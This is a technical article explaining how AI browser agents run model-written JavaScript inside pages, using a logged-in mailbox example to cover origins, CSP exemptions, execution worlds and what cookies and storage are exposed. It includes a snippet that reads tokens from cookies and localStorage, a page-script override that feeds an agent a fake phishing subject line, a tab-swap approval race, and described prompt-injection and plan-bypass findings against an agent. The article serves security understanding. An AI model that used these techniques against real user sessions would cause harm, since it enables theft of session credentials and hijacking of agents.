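# In-page JavaScript execution as a tool for AI agents: what the code can read, change and reach

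## What an in-page JavaScript tool is and which browser rules it inherits

A browser agent is a program in which a large language model operates a web browser on a user's behalf. The user types a request in ordinary language, and the model chooses which pages to open, what to click and what to type. Many browser agents also have an in-page JavaScript tool, which lets the model write code in JavaScript, the programming language that websites use to make their pages interactive. The agent's software runs that code inside the page open in a tab and returns the result to the model.

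Code that an agent runs in a page has the same powers as the page's own scripts. The browser confines those scripts to one website and blocks them from the computer's files and programs, so the tool can do much less than one that runs code directly on the machine. But the code also acts within the user's logged-in session, and most of the possible harm to a mailbox or bank account can be done through that session.

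### The agent loop

A language model only produces text, so ordinary software has to do the clicking. The steps in Anthropic's *Browser use tool*, documentation for programmers who connect the company's Claude models to a browser, are typical:

1. The application sends the model the user's request and a list of tools, each with a name and the inputs it takes.
2. The model replies with one or more tool calls, for example one that opens an address and one that reads the page.
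3. The application runs the calls in order, stops if one fails, and sends back a result for each.
4. The model reads the results. It then either makes further calls, which leads back to step 3, or answers the user in plain text.

All the model's information about the page comes from those results. Some tools return a screenshot, and others return the accessibility tree, a text outline of the page like the one screen readers use. A line such as `button "Search" [ref_4]` stands for one element, which the model can click by giving its reference, `ref_4`.

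An in-page JavaScript tool is one more entry in the list. The shortest useful call asks for the page's title. It appears as the first example of the tool `browser_evaluate` in Playwright's *Code Execution*, a page of the manual for Microsoft's browser automation software:

```
browser_evaluate { function: "() => document.title" }
"TodoMVC - React"
```

The first line is the call, a small function that returns `document.title`, the property that holds the page's title. The second line is the result, here from a demonstration to-do list. The model could use the same call format for a function that lists every link, empties a text field or presses a send button.

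### Tools in current products

`browser_evaluate` is a tool in Playwright MCP, a server that offers tools to a language model through a shared standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). The model can use it to run a JavaScript function on the whole page or on one element that it names. Glama's *browser_evaluate*, an entry in a public directory of MCP servers, labels the tool "Destructive". The label is fair because the same call can run code that reads a page or code that alters it.

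Google's counterpart is `evaluate_script`, a tool in an MCP server built on Chrome DevTools, the Chrome browser's inspection panels for web developers. Google released the server as Chrome DevTools MCP, and its Chrome for Developers site now calls it Chrome DevTools for agents, though the software package is still `chrome-devtools-mcp`. The project's README lists `evaluate_script` among the debugging tools. Even the introductory examples in its tool reference go beyond reading what is on the screen, since one sample function returns `document.title` and another calls `fetch`, the browser's command for sending a network request.

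Anthropic has the tool in two products. One is Claude in Chrome, an extension that puts the Claude model in a side panel next to the user's own tabs. *Claude for Chrome Extension Internals (v1.0.56)*, an unofficial reading of the extension's source code by sshh12 (2026), gives the description of `javascript_tool` that the model receives. It says the model's code can work with the DOM (document object model, the browser's live tree of page elements, which scripts can read and change), the variables of the page's own scripts, and the `window` object, which represents the browser window to scripts. *Claude in Chrome*, a threat analysis by the security research group Zenity Labs, reports the same ability, based on a list of tools its researchers extracted from the extension's system prompt. Any update to the extension can change its tools, so the description from version 1.0.56 may not match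 other versions.

Anthropic's other product, a toolset for programmers, includes a tool called `javascript_exec` that does the same job. It is one of four tools, out of 31, that stay off until the programmer enables them. Anthropic says this tool and file uploads are off by default because both expand what a manipulated page could make Claude do.

The source code of Chromium (2026), the open-source project on which Chrome builds, also contains a JavaScript tool for the AI assistant in DevTools, the browser's developer panels. The model may use the tool to gather information or modify the page, and must supply a title and an explanation with every snippet.

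### Why agents get the tool

An agent that can already click, type and read the page might seem to need nothing more. Playwright's manual has a table that matches eight tasks to tools, and three of the tasks indeed need no code: clicking a button, filling a form field and reading an element's text all have tools of their own. Only one row recommends `browser_evaluate`, and that row is for checking computed styles. (The other four, among them multi-step logic and custom waiting conditions, go to `browser_run_code_unsafe`, which runs outside the page.)

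Computed styles are the final values for colour, size, position and visibility that the browser works out after applying all of a page's style rules. The accessibility tree leaves most of them out. For example, it lists a button with white text on a white background like any other button. In a screenshot, the model would see an empty patch and couldn't tell why, but one line of JavaScript would return both colours.

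Playwright gives two more sample calls of this kind. One returns an attribute that the page's programmers attached to a button as a label for testing, and the other returns the size of the visible area, 1280 by 720 pixels. The sample code in Chromium measures the rectangle of every element on the page, keeps those that overlap the element under inspection, and returns their names and stacking order. This is useful for finding out why a click has no effect, since an invisible layer may be covering the button. An agent with only clicks and snapshots would have to guess the cause.

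Beyer (2026), in *Unlock runtime insights*, a Google announcement for developers, adds three reasons that concern efficiency more than visibility:

- The model can combine several steps in one execution.
- Code in the page can work on objects that can't travel to the model. Results leave the page as text, and a live component of a web framework doesn't survive the conversion. A function can examine the component where it is and return only the answer.
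- Fewer calls mean fewer round trips between the agent and the browser. To add up 200 rows of a table, a function needs one call.

These are good reasons, but they come from debugging and testing. They apply less to an agent that books a table or tidies an inbox, since it can do most of that work by clicking and typing. General-purpose agents such as Claude in Chrome also come with the tool, and the pages they work on are mostly other people's websites where the user has accounts.

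### Origin and the same-origin policy

The main limit on any page script is the same-origin policy, which is older than browser agents. The CS 161 textbook's *Same-Origin Policy*, from a computer security course at Berkeley, explains the need for the rule with the example of a user who has a mailbox open in one tab and a malicious site in another. Without some barrier, the malicious site could read the mail or send messages in the user's name.

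The barrier depends on the notion of an origin. The origin of a page is the combination of the scheme, the host name and the port number in its address. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, write this for a page *w* as

o(*w*) = (scheme(*w*), host(*w*), port(*w*)).

The scheme is the part before the colon, usually `https` or its unencrypted predecessor `http`. The port is a number that identifies the service on the server that the browser is connecting to. Addresses normally omit it, and the browser uses 443 for `https` and 80 for `http`. The page `https://mail.example/inbox` therefore has the origin (https, mail.example, 443), which does not include the path `/inbox`.

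The same-origin policy is the browser rule that stops a script of one origin from reading the data of another. Two origins match only if all three parts match. For a script on `https://mail.example/inbox` the comparisons come out as follows:

| Page the script tries to read | What differs | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `https://mail.example/settings` | only the path | allowed |
| `http://mail.example/inbox` | scheme, and with it the port | refused |
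| `https://login.mail.example/inbox` | host name | refused |
| `https://mail.example:8443/inbox` | port | refused |

The third row surprises people because the same company presumably runs both hosts. web.dev's *"Same-site" and "same-origin"* defines two addresses as "same-site" if they share the scheme and the registered domain, even if their subdomains differ. Some browser rules use this looser test, but the same-origin policy does not.

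W3C's *Same Origin Policy* opens with the statement "There is no single same-origin policy." Each browser interface applies the idea differently, so the rule for reading another page's elements differs in detail from the rule for reading a server's response to a network request. The common aim is to let people visit an untrustworthy site without that site interfering with their sessions on other sites.

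### Every script on a page has the page's origin

When a browser loads a page, it creates an environment for the page's scripts and labels that environment with the page's origin. Data also carries origin labels. According to Wang and colleagues, a script may access a piece of data only if the data's label matches that of the script's environment.

A script gets its origin from the page it runs on, regardless of which server supplied the file. If the mail site loads a visitor-counting script from `https://stats.example` with a script tag, the script runs with the origin of `https://mail.example` and can read and change whatever the mail site's own code can. The same goes for advertising code, chat widgets and any other third-party script included this way. A frame, however, is a separate page embedded in the first, so it has its own origin. An advertisement loaded in a frame from the advertiser's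 server runs with the advertiser's origin.

The browser treats code from an in-page JavaScript tool like the visitor-counting script. Its check compares only origins, so it doesn't matter that a language model wrote the code. Anthropic says that code the model runs through `javascript_exec` has every privilege of the page, including access to cookies and stored data and the ability to send requests to the page's own origin.

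In cross-site scripting (XSS), an attacker gets a script into a page of someone else's website, and the browser runs it as if the site had written it. Zenity Labs calls the JavaScript tool in Claude in Chrome "XSS as-a-service". The comparison is accurate about privileges, since the tool's code also runs under the site's origin, but it overstates the attacker's control. In XSS the attacker's code runs directly, whereas here the attacker has to get a model to write or pass on the code, and the model may refuse.

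In indirect prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in content that an agent reads, and the agent follows them as if the user had given them. Wang and colleagues give the example of a user who asks the agent to post a harmless comment on a software issue, when the text of the issue includes a command for the agent to ignore its instructions and click a link.

### A logged-in mailbox as the running example

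How much this matters depends on the session the code runs in. Programmers who use Anthropic's toolset choose the browser themselves, and Anthropic advises them to enable `javascript_exec` only in sessions that hold no credentials. By default, Chrome DevTools for agents starts a browser with a profile folder separate from the user's everyday one, but it can also connect to a Chrome that is already running.

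With Anthropic's extension, by contrast, Claude shares the browser's login state and can access any site where the user is already signed in, according to Anthropic's *Use Claude Code with Chrome*, which covers the link between the extension and the company's coding agent. Zenity Labs objected that the extension has no switch to turn this off. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome* describes an alternative added since then. People new to browser use get a browser built into Claude by default, while existing users of the extension stay in their own Chrome unless they change the setting. For those existing users, the advice to keep the JavaScript tool away from credentials is hard to reconcile with the product's purpose, which is to work on pages where the user has logged in.

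An invented case makes the consequences concrete. A user has logged in to a mail service at `https://mail.example` and asks an agent in that tab to summarise the unread messages. The agent has an in-page JavaScript tool. The tab holds the messages themselves and five other things of interest:

| Item | Where it is | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Session cookie `sid` | cookie with the HttpOnly mark | proves to the server that the user has logged in |
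| Preference cookie `theme` | ordinary cookie | stores the choice of a dark or light display |
| Access token | `localStorage` | authorises requests to the mail service's programming interface |
| Anti-forgery token | a meta tag in the page | shows the server that a request came from its own page |
| Payment frame | embedded page from `https://pay.example` | lets the user pay for extra storage |

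A cookie is a small piece of text that a website stores in the browser and that the browser sends back with later requests. If a cookie is marked HttpOnly, the browser still sends it but hides it from page scripts. `localStorage` stores named values, which the browser keeps separately for each origin. A meta tag is an invisible element that holds information about the page. The frame from `https://pay.example` appears in the middle of the mail page but has a different origin because its host name differs.

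When the model sends a function to this tab, the function runs with the origin (https, mail.example, 443), in a session that the mail server already accepts as the user's. The damage one call can do depends on what the code can read, what it can change, and which servers it can reach.

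## How model-written code gets into the page and returns a result

Suppose the user of the mailbox at `https://mail.example` asks for the subject lines of the unread messages. The model replies with a tool call that contains this string:

```
() => [...document.querySelectorAll(".unread .subject")].map(e => e.textContent)
```

The function returns a list of the subject lines of all unread messages. The agent's software must then get the browser to run the string as code. Chrome has three main ways to do that: a command in the protocol behind DevTools, and two programming interfaces for browser extensions. They run the code in different environments, and a site's security policy can block it with some of these methods but not others.

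### Through the DevTools protocol

The Chrome DevTools Protocol (CDP) is an interface that lets outside programs inspect and control a Chromium browser. Its `Runtime.evaluate` command runs JavaScript in a page and requires only the code, passed as a string. ChromeDriver, a program that test software uses to control Chrome, sends all its JavaScript through this command, according to Chromium's *Run JavaScript Code*.

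The source code of Puppeteer, a browser automation library from Google (2017), contains the whole trip:

1. Puppeteer receives the string and adds a comment that names its source, which helps with error messages.
2. It sends the string to the browser with the number of an execution context, meaning one particular JavaScript environment. Each frame on a page has its own.
3. The browser runs the code in that context.
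4. The browser sends back a result or a description of the error, and Puppeteer converts it into an ordinary value.

The string in the example defines a function without calling it, so `Runtime.evaluate` would return the function itself without collecting any subject lines. The software must either add the call or use `Runtime.callFunctionOn`, a related command that takes a function and its arguments. Puppeteer uses that command whenever it receives a function.

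According to Playwright's *Evaluating JavaScript*, the automation program and the page run in separate processes, possibly on separate computers, so a variable in one does not exist in the other. To use data from elsewhere, such as an order number from an earlier page, the model has to write it into the code string or pass it as an argument.

Puppeteer also sets an option called `userGesture`, which makes the browser treat the code as if the user had started it. In Chromium, the function behind this option is called `pretendUserGesture`. Browsers reserve some features, such as opening a new window, for code that follows a real click or key press. A page's own scripts can't set this option, so the tool's code can do slightly more than they can here.

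### Through a browser extension

An extension can inject code with `chrome.scripting`, which Google's documentation now calls `browser.scripting`. According to Chrome for Developers' *browser.scripting*, its `executeScript()` method accepts a file from the extension's package or a function in the extension's code, but not a string. This suits an agent's fixed operations, such as clicking a button, which the programmer wrote in advance. To run a string of code that the model has just written, the extension has to inject a fixed function that takes the string as an argument and passes it to `eval`, the JavaScript function that runs text as code.

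Zenity Labs lists `scripting` among the permissions of Claude in Chrome. The permission alone doesn't show that the extension's JavaScript tool uses this route, because fixed functions for reading and clicking need it too.

The other interface, `chrome.userScripts`, is for code that doesn't come with the extension. Its `execute()` method takes a string and has been in Chrome since version 135. Mozilla has added it to Firefox 153, according to robwu in *Implement userScripts.execute*. The extension's permissions aren't enough to use the interface. Chrome for Developers' *browser.userScripts* explains that each user also has to open the extension's details page and turn on "Allow User Scripts" (before Chrome 138, users had to turn on the browser's developer mode instead). This extra step is an obstacle for a product with a mass audience.

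Both interfaces inject code into the tab's main frame by default. With the `allFrames` option, the code runs in every frame that the extension has permission for, and each frame returns a separate result. In the mailbox, that could include the payment frame from `https://pay.example`, which the mail page's scripts can't read. The same-origin policy still applies to each copy of the code, but the extension receives the results from both origins.

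### Main world and isolated world

A page can contain several JavaScript environments, called worlds. The page's own scripts share the main world. An isolated world shares the page's DOM but has its own variables. `chrome.scripting` uses an isolated world unless the programmer asks for the main one, and `chrome.userScripts` has its own isolated world called `USER_SCRIPT`. CDP runs code in the main world by default, though a client can choose another context.

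Chrome for Developers' *Content scripts* demonstrates the separation with a single button. The page's script sets a variable `greeting` to "hello, " and attaches the name Bob to the button. An extension's script sets its own `greeting` to "hola, " and attaches the name Roberto to the same button. When the user clicks, two messages appear in turn, one greeting Bob and the other Roberto. Neither script overwrote the other's variable or the name the other had attached to the button.

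Programmers can run code in the isolated world without realizing it. Lajoie (2023), in *executeScript function can't access full window/globalThis object*, injected a function there to read one of the page's global variables and got `undefined`, although the variable was visible in the browser's console.

For the mailbox, the two worlds compare as follows:

| Item | Code in the main world | Code in an isolated world |
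|---|---|---|
| Variables and functions of the mail site's scripts | can read and change | can't see |
| Messages and anti-forgery token in the DOM | can read and change | can read and change |
| Preference cookie `theme` | can read and change | can read and change |
| HttpOnly session cookie `sid` | can't read | can't read |
| Access token in `localStorage` | can read and change | can read and change |

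Only the first row differs, because cookies and `localStorage` belong to the document and its origin, and both worlds work on the same document. Isolation therefore protects the tool's variables from the page but does very little to protect the page's data from the tool. If a mail site held a decrypted message in a variable, isolated code couldn't read it until the text appeared on the screen. But the isolated code could add a script element to the shared DOM, and the browser would run that script in the main world unless a security policy blocked it.

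### What a Content Security Policy stops

A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a site's list of the sources its pages may load from, run code from or connect to. Many sites use it to limit the damage from cross-site scripting, and a strict policy also forbids `eval`. That ban may keep an agent's tool from running the model's string. If the code does run, the page's policy may still limit the requests it makes.

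| Route and world | Does a page's ban on `eval` stop the string? | Does the page's CSP limit the code's requests? |
|---|---|---|
| CDP, main world | no | yes, by default |
| `chrome.scripting`, main world | yes | yes |
| `chrome.scripting`, isolated world | the world's own ban stops it on every site | no, going by the world's own policy |
| `chrome.userScripts`, `USER_SCRIPT` world | no | no |

Chromium's CDP definition gives `Runtime.evaluate` a setting, `allowUnsafeEvalBlockedByCSP`, which is on by default and lets `eval` calls inside the model's code succeed even when the page's CSP would block them. A code change by kozy, in *[DevTools] Bring back bypassing CSP for eval in Runtime.evaluate*, restored this exemption because programs such as ChromeDriver relied on it. `Runtime.callFunctionOn` has no setting to turn the exemption off.

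The exemption is narrow. A Playwright test, in a copy on GitLink, opens a page whose CSP forbids added scripts and tries to insert a script element that sets a variable to 42. The test then reads the variable with `page.evaluate()` and gets `undefined`, so the policy blocked the script element but not the code sent through the automation command. The rest of the policy also stays in force, including the list of servers the page may connect to. Playwright's `bypassCSP` option lifts the whole policy but is off by default. Puppeteer has a similar option, the *Page.setBypassCSP() method*, which a program should normally call before it opens the site, because the browser applies the bypass when it sets up the policy.

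With `chrome.scripting`, the `eval` workaround mostly fails. Isolated worlds have their own CSP, which forbids `eval` even if the page allows it. Oliver Dunk of Google confirmed this to Likely Logic (2025), in *User Scripts vs injected scripts with eval()*, and recommended `chrome.userScripts` instead. In the main world the page's CSP applies, so the workaround succeeds on sites that allow `eval` and fails on sites that forbid it, as banks and mail services have good reason to do.

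The `USER_SCRIPT` world is exempt from the page's CSP, so the model's string runs there, but any `eval` inside it fails until the extension loosens the world's own CSP. According to a comment in Firefox's tests, on Searchfox, loosening it is the most common scenario for extensions of this type. If the world already exists in an open document, the new policy takes effect there only after a reload, according to MDN's *userScripts.configureWorld()*. Chrome's documentation gives the exemption only for the `USER_SCRIPT` world, so the page's CSP probably applies when an extension uses the interface in the main world.

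The right-hand column of the table matters for safety because an isolated world's policy restricts scripts and plug-in objects but not connections. If a programmer moves the model's code out of the main world to shield it from the page, the site's own limit on where code may send data no longer applies to it.

### Turning the result into text

The browser can return a result in two forms. In one, the object stays in the page and the outside program gets a reference to it, which it can use in later commands. In the other, the browser converts the object to JSON, a plain text format for lists, numbers, strings and named values, and sends a copy. A language model needs the copy. For the mailbox it might be:

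```
["Invoice for May", "Lunch on Friday?"]
```

Lists and strings convert well, but many other values don't. A field whose value is `undefined` disappears, so `{a: undefined}` arrives as `{}`. If the browser reports that it can't convert an object, Puppeteer replaces the object with `undefined`. The library's tests, also on Searchfox, check this behaviour. A few numbers that JSON can't express, such as infinity and "not a number", are sent in a separate field made for them.

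This means `undefined` can mislead an agent. The function may have returned nothing, found an object that couldn't be passed back, or looked for a page variable from an isolated world, as Lajoie's did. A model that concludes "the variable doesn't exist" could be wrong in the last two cases. It is safer for the code to return only the strings and numbers the agent needs.

Some code can't return its result immediately. A function that requests data from a server returns a promise, an object that stands for a value that isn't available yet. An example in Playwright's manual fetches the current page again and returns the response's status code. Playwright and both extension interfaces wait for the promise to settle before they return a value. `Runtime.evaluate` waits only if the program sets `awaitPromise`, which Puppeteer always does.

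If the tab moves to another page while Puppeteer is waiting for the function's result, Puppeteer reports "Execution context was destroyed, most likely because of a navigation." The error means only that no result came back. The function may already have sent an email, for example, and a model that takes the error to mean nothing happened may send it again.

### Why the software can't trust the result

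JavaScript lets scripts replace most of the language's built-in functions. Playwright's manual uses this for testing: one line, `Math.random = () => 42`, makes the random number generator return 42 every time. A page's scripts can do the same to functions that the model's code depends on. In the mailbox, the visitor-counting script from `https://stats.example` runs in the main world, and its owner could add this line:

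```
document.querySelectorAll = () => [{ textContent: "Account locked: sign in at mail-help.example" }];
```

The model's function hasn't changed, but it now returns this one false subject line. The script could also have written a fake message into the DOM, but the user might notice it on the screen. When the script replaces a function instead, the page looks normal and only the agent gets the false answer. The replacement also receives whatever the model's code passes to it, so if the code passed a private note to a function replaced this way, the note would reach the script's owner.

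A Mozilla engineer wrote in *Support execution world MAIN in `scripting.executeScript()` and content_scripts* that the main world is untrusted and that an extension can't trust anything that comes out of it.

An isolated world fixes part of this. *PSA*, an announcement to Chrome extension developers, points out that code on the page can't change the global values that an isolated script uses. `document.querySelectorAll` would therefore return the real subject lines. The isolated world guarantees that the code reads the DOM correctly, but the text in the DOM may still be false or harmful, since anyone can email the user and choose the subject line. Chrome for Developers' *Stay secure*, written for an older version of the extension platform, tells programmers to assume that an attacker might have crafted any message from a script in a page.

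The risk is greatest when the agent's software relies on such a result for a security decision. Suppose it guards each call with a line of its own in the main world:

```
if (!["https://mail.example"].includes(location.origin)) return;
```

Browsers don't let a page replace `location`, but the page can replace `includes`, the function that searches the list, with one that always returns `true`.

### When the tab changes between approval and execution

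Some checks happen outside the page. An agent might look up the tab's address, ask the user for permission to run code on that site, and then run the code. This leaves a gap between the check and the code running, which security engineers call a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw.

Suppose the user has a recipe site open at `https://recipes.example`, and the model writes `() => document.body.innerText`, which returns all the visible text. The call is harmless on a recipe page.

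1. The software finds that tab 7 shows `https://recipes.example` and asks the user to approve the call for that site.
2. While the question is on the screen, a script on the recipe page sends the tab to `https://mail.example/inbox`. The user is logged in, so the inbox loads.
3. The user clicks "allow" for `https://recipes.example`.
4. The software sends the function to tab 7.
5. The browser runs it in the document that tab 7 now holds and returns the text of the inbox.

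The same-origin policy doesn't prevent this, because the function runs with the mail site's origin and reads only the mail site's page, which the policy permits. The software made the mistake by checking one document and then addressing its command to the tab rather than to that document. The same mistake could also let code that the user approved for the mailbox, with the text of a private reply written into it, run on a hostile page that has replaced the functions the code calls.

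Many interfaces make it easy to run code in the wrong page. `chrome.scripting` requires only a tab ID to identify the target. CDP runs the code in the current page if the program doesn't specify a context. Playwright's `browser_evaluate` has a field for an element but none for the expected origin. Naming an element doesn't reliably prevent this mistake, because a selector such as `button` will match something on almost any page.

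Zenity Labs found a related gap in Claude in Chrome. In the mode that asks before acting, the extension shows the user a plan listing the sites it expects to visit. The researchers approved a plan to summarise the open page, and the agent then went to Wikipedia, which was not on the list. The test shows that the part of the software that carries out actions can fail to enforce the plan approved in the side panel. It doesn't demonstrate the attack above, because it involved a harmless navigation and no JavaScript call.

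A correct check has to bind the approval to the exact code and its arguments, the document in which the code will run, that document's origin, and the world. The browser must then refuse to run the code anywhere else. Chrome has the parts for this:

- Since version 106, `chrome.scripting` has accepted `documentIds`, which name particular documents instead of whatever a tab contains. `userScripts.execute()` accepts them too.
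- CDP describes each context with its origin and a unique identifier, so a program can take both from the same record. It can then pass the identifier to `Runtime.evaluate` as `uniqueContextId`. Chromium added this option, which it still marks as experimental, to prevent code from running in the wrong context after a navigation.

The older `contextId`, which Puppeteer sends, is less reliable because different browser processes may reuse the same number. The extension interfaces also return the `documentId` of the document where the code ran. Comparing it with the approved `documentId` shows whether the code ran in the wrong document, but only after execution.

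With a proper binding, the call in step 4 fails because the recipe document is gone. The software then has to treat the mailbox as a new case and ask again. If it just retried the call on the tab's current document, it would bring back the flaw.

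## What the code can read in the page, its cookies and its storage

Once a function runs in the inbox at `https://mail.example`, it can read nearly everything that the mail site's own code can read. That includes the messages, the contents of forms, most cookies and all the data the site keeps in the browser. The HttpOnly session cookie, the payment frame, other sites' tabs, the browser's saved passwords and the files on the computer stay closed to it. One short call can test four of these items:

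```
() => ({
  csrf: document.querySelector('meta[name="csrf-token"]').content,
  cookies: document.cookie,
  token: localStorage.getItem("access_token"),
  frame: document.querySelector("iframe").contentDocument
})
```

The result might be:

```
{ "csrf": "8f1c27", "cookies": "theme=dark", "token": "eyJhbGci", "frame": null }
```

The anti-forgery token and the access token come back as plain text. The cookie string contains `theme` but not `sid`, and the browser returns `null` in place of the payment frame's document. For code in the main world, the whole mailbox looks like this:

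| Item | Can the code read it? | Why |
|---|---|---|
| Messages on the page, visible or hidden | yes | they are in the DOM |
| Anti-forgery token in the meta tag | yes | it is in the DOM |
| Unsent draft, filled-in password field | yes | scripts can read a field's `value` |
| Variables of the mail site's scripts | some | only global variables are within reach |
| Preference cookie `theme` | yes | it has no HttpOnly mark |
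| Session cookie `sid` | no | the browser leaves HttpOnly cookies out of `document.cookie` |
| Access token in `localStorage` | yes | the storage belongs to the page's origin |
| Data in `sessionStorage` | yes, for this tab | same origin, but each tab has its own copy |
| Offline mail in IndexedDB or Cache storage | yes | both belong to the page's origin |
| Print preview in a frame from `https://mail.example` | yes | same origin |
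| Payment frame from `https://pay.example` | no | different origin |
| Second mailbox tab that the user opened | not its page, but the storage they share | the code has no reference to that tab |
| Tab with the user's bank | no | different origin, and no reference |
| Passwords saved in the browser | no | pages have no command for listing them |
| Files on the computer | only files the user has picked for the page | pages can't open a file by its path |

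### Page elements and form fields

A script can read every ordinary element in its document, including those that don't appear on the screen. The `innerText` property returns roughly the text that the page displays, while `textContent` also returns hidden text. In the mailbox, `textContent` might include collapsed quoted replies, or contacts loaded for a menu the user never opened. The script can also read HTML comments and attributes that the page doesn't display. A user watching the tab therefore can't tell how much a call has read.

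Some page components keep their contents in a closed shadow root, a part of the DOM that ordinary scripts outside the component can't access. Few sites use it to protect private data, since it exists mainly to stop one component's code from interfering with another's.

A form field's `value` property holds the field's current contents, including a draft the user hasn't sent. A password field shows dots, but its `value` is the password in plain text.

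The browser can also fill in a form with a saved address, card number or password, and scripts can then read those values like any others. In Chrome, a login form can look complete right after the page loads, but scripts get an empty string for the saved password until the user first clicks or presses a key. A click that an agent simulates probably counts too. The code can't open the browser's password store, but it can read a password that the browser has filled in.

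### Script variables

In the main world, the code can use the page's global variables and functions. An example in Playwright's manual calls `window.myApp.use(data)`, where `myApp` is an object that belongs to the page's application. Such an object might contain the user's name, account number or messages that the site has decrypted.

Code outside a function or JavaScript module cannot directly read the variables inside it, because it cannot refer to them by name. This rule is meant to keep programs organized and is a weak security barrier. If the mail site keeps a token in a private variable and passes it to `fetch` with each request, code in the main world can replace `fetch` and read the token the next time it is used.

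### Cookies and the HttpOnly mark

`document.cookie` returns one string with the names and values of the cookies that apply to the page, such as `theme=dark; lang=en`. It leaves out their expiry dates and security settings.

Cookies don't follow the same-origin policy exactly. *Measuring Web Session Security at Scale* (Calzavara, Jonker and colleagues) explains that browsers normally share a cookie across ports and across `http` and `https`. The browser sends a cookie only to the host that set it, unless that host sets it for a parent domain. If `login.mail.example` sets a cookie for all of `mail.example`, code in the inbox can read that cookie, even though the same-origin policy stops the code from reading the login page. These loose rules date from the early web. *Cookies* (Bingler, West and Wilander, 2025), a draft of the revised cookie standard, acknowledges that cookies have many historical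 flaws that weaken security and privacy.

The HttpOnly mark is stricter and applies to every script on the page. In a small test in Microsoft's developer documentation, *HttpCookie.HttpOnly Property*, a script looks up two cookies by name. It gets the value of the unmarked cookie but `null` for the one marked HttpOnly.

Two other common cookie settings, `Secure` and `SameSite`, don't affect which cookies code in the mailbox page can read. `Secure` limits a cookie to encrypted connections, which the mailbox uses anyway, and `SameSite` controls whether the browser sends a cookie with requests that come from other sites. *Least Privilege Access for Persistent Storage Mechanisms in Web Browsers* (Kancherla, Goel and Bichhawat, 2024) states that `HttpOnly` is the only cookie attribute that prevents all JavaScript from accessing a cookie.

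The HttpOnly mark restricts code in the page but not the software that put the code there. The DevTools protocol command `Network.getCookies` returns HttpOnly cookies along with the rest, and an extension with the `cookies` permission can get them too. If an agent's developer gives the model a separate tool for reading cookies, the model can read HttpOnly cookies such as `sid`.

### Web storage, IndexedDB and Cache storage

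Browsers offer sites several larger stores. `sessionStorage` works like `localStorage`, and the two together are called web storage. The main difference is that `localStorage` keeps its contents indefinitely, while the browser deletes `sessionStorage` when the user closes the tab or the browser (Ahmad, Casarin and Calzavara, 2022, *An Empirical Analysis of Web Storage and its Applications to Web Tracking*). IndexedDB is a database for larger amounts of data. Cache storage holds saved server responses, which a site can use to work offline.

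For all four, the page's origin decides what a script can read. The code doesn't even need to know what it is looking for:

- `Object.entries(localStorage)` returns every name and value, and the same call works for `sessionStorage`.
- `indexedDB.databases()` lists the databases, which the code can then open and search.
- `caches.keys()` lists the caches. The code can read the saved responses in them, apart from responses that came from another origin without permission for scripts to read them.

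Cookies and storage can hold more than the page displays. A mail service that works offline might store months of messages in IndexedDB, and code that an agent runs in the inbox page could read all of them without opening any.

None of these stores has an equivalent of HttpOnly. Kancherla and colleagues point out that sites cannot mark a value in web storage or IndexedDB as closed to scripts. A site can remove the `localStorage` property from its window, but a script can still reach the same data by adding an empty frame to the page, because the frame has the page's origin and its own working `localStorage` property.

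Third-party scripts already use this access heavily. In March and April 2024, Kancherla and colleagues ran a modified Firefox on the 10,000 most popular sites and logged each time a script read or wrote stored data. Third-party scripts accounted for 90% of the cookie accesses, 91% of the `localStorage` accesses and 72% of the IndexedDB accesses. The agent's tool also runs code that can read this data, and the site's owner hasn't seen that code.

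### Frames, windows and other tabs

A page's script can also read other documents of the same origin if it has a reference to them, for example because the page embeds them in frames or opened them in windows. According to Mozilla's *Script Security*, objects with the same origin can access each other freely in Firefox. If the mail site shows a print preview in a frame from its own address, the tool's code can read the preview as well as the inbox.

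The browser limits what code can read from a document of another origin. Mozilla's documentation, in a copy on Searchfox, describes a wrapper that denies access to everything except a few properties of the window and its address. Code in the inbox can count the frames inside the payment frame or check whether a pop-up window has closed, but it can't read either one's text, forms or cookies.

The payment frame's own code can send data across this barrier. Rautenstrauch, Mitkov and colleagues' study of website security before and after login, *To Auth or Not To Auth*, describes `postMessage`, a browser function that lets documents of different origins exchange messages. If the frame sends "payment complete, card ending 4417" to the mail page, any script on that page can listen for the message, and so can the agent's code.

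The code has no reference to tabs that the user opened separately, so it can't read their pages or their `sessionStorage`, even if one of them has the same mailbox open. But two tabs with the same mailbox share cookies, `localStorage`, IndexedDB and Cache storage. If the second tab saves a draft in `localStorage`, code running in the first tab can read it.

### Saved passwords and local files

Page code can't list the browser's saved passwords or open a local file by its path, because the browser gives it no command for either. The browser also runs page code in a process that the operating system bars from most of the disk.

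The browser stores cookies, web storage and passwords in the user's profile, which is a folder on the computer's disk. A program on the computer may be able to open this folder, but JavaScript in a page can't. Many people don't know that the profile is stored locally. *User Profiles*, a 2025 study of attacks on these folders, included a survey in which only seven participants correctly answered that the browser keeps the profile on the local disk. Another 14 thought it was in the cloud, and 17 thought it was in both places.

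The user can give a page access to individual files. When the user attaches a tax return to an email, the mail page's scripts and the agent's code can both read the file as soon as the user selects it, before the email is sent.

### Why a token in localStorage is more exposed

The mail server may accept either the access token or the session cookie `sid` for the same actions, but the code can copy only the token.

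`localStorage.getItem("access_token")` returns the token as text, which the tool passes to the model. Even without an attack, a model debugging a page that won't load might read everything in `localStorage`, including the token. Anyone who obtains the token may be able to use it from another computer until it expires, even after the user has closed the tab. With `sid`, the code can at most send requests from the user's browser, which attaches the cookie without revealing it.

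A stolen copy can still work after the user logs out. Calzavara and colleagues logged out of 3,302 sites and then tried the old session cookies. The cookies still worked after five minutes on 18% of the sites, and after ten days on 14%. The test used cookies, but a server that doesn't cancel a session at logout is unlikely to cancel a token either.

Most published advice is against storing login tokens in `localStorage`. pilcrow (2023), a programmer's blog, quotes such a recommendation from OWASP, a software security non-profit, but notes that large sites such as Discord keep everything there.

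An agent's code runs inside the page, after the encrypted connection has delivered everything, so whether it can copy a session token depends on HttpOnly. In *Web Storage*, a 2016 post for the security company PortSwigger, Kettle argues that web storage, though flawed, is a better place than cookies for session tokens. One of his reasons is that web storage keeps the `https` and `http` versions of a site apart, while a cookie needs the `Secure` setting for this. He is right, but this reason concerns an attacker who listens in on the network.

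### How many sites use HttpOnly

If a site doesn't mark its session cookie `HttpOnly`, in-page code can copy the cookie as easily as a token in `localStorage`. Measurements of how often sites omit the mark seem to differ widely, mostly because they count different things.

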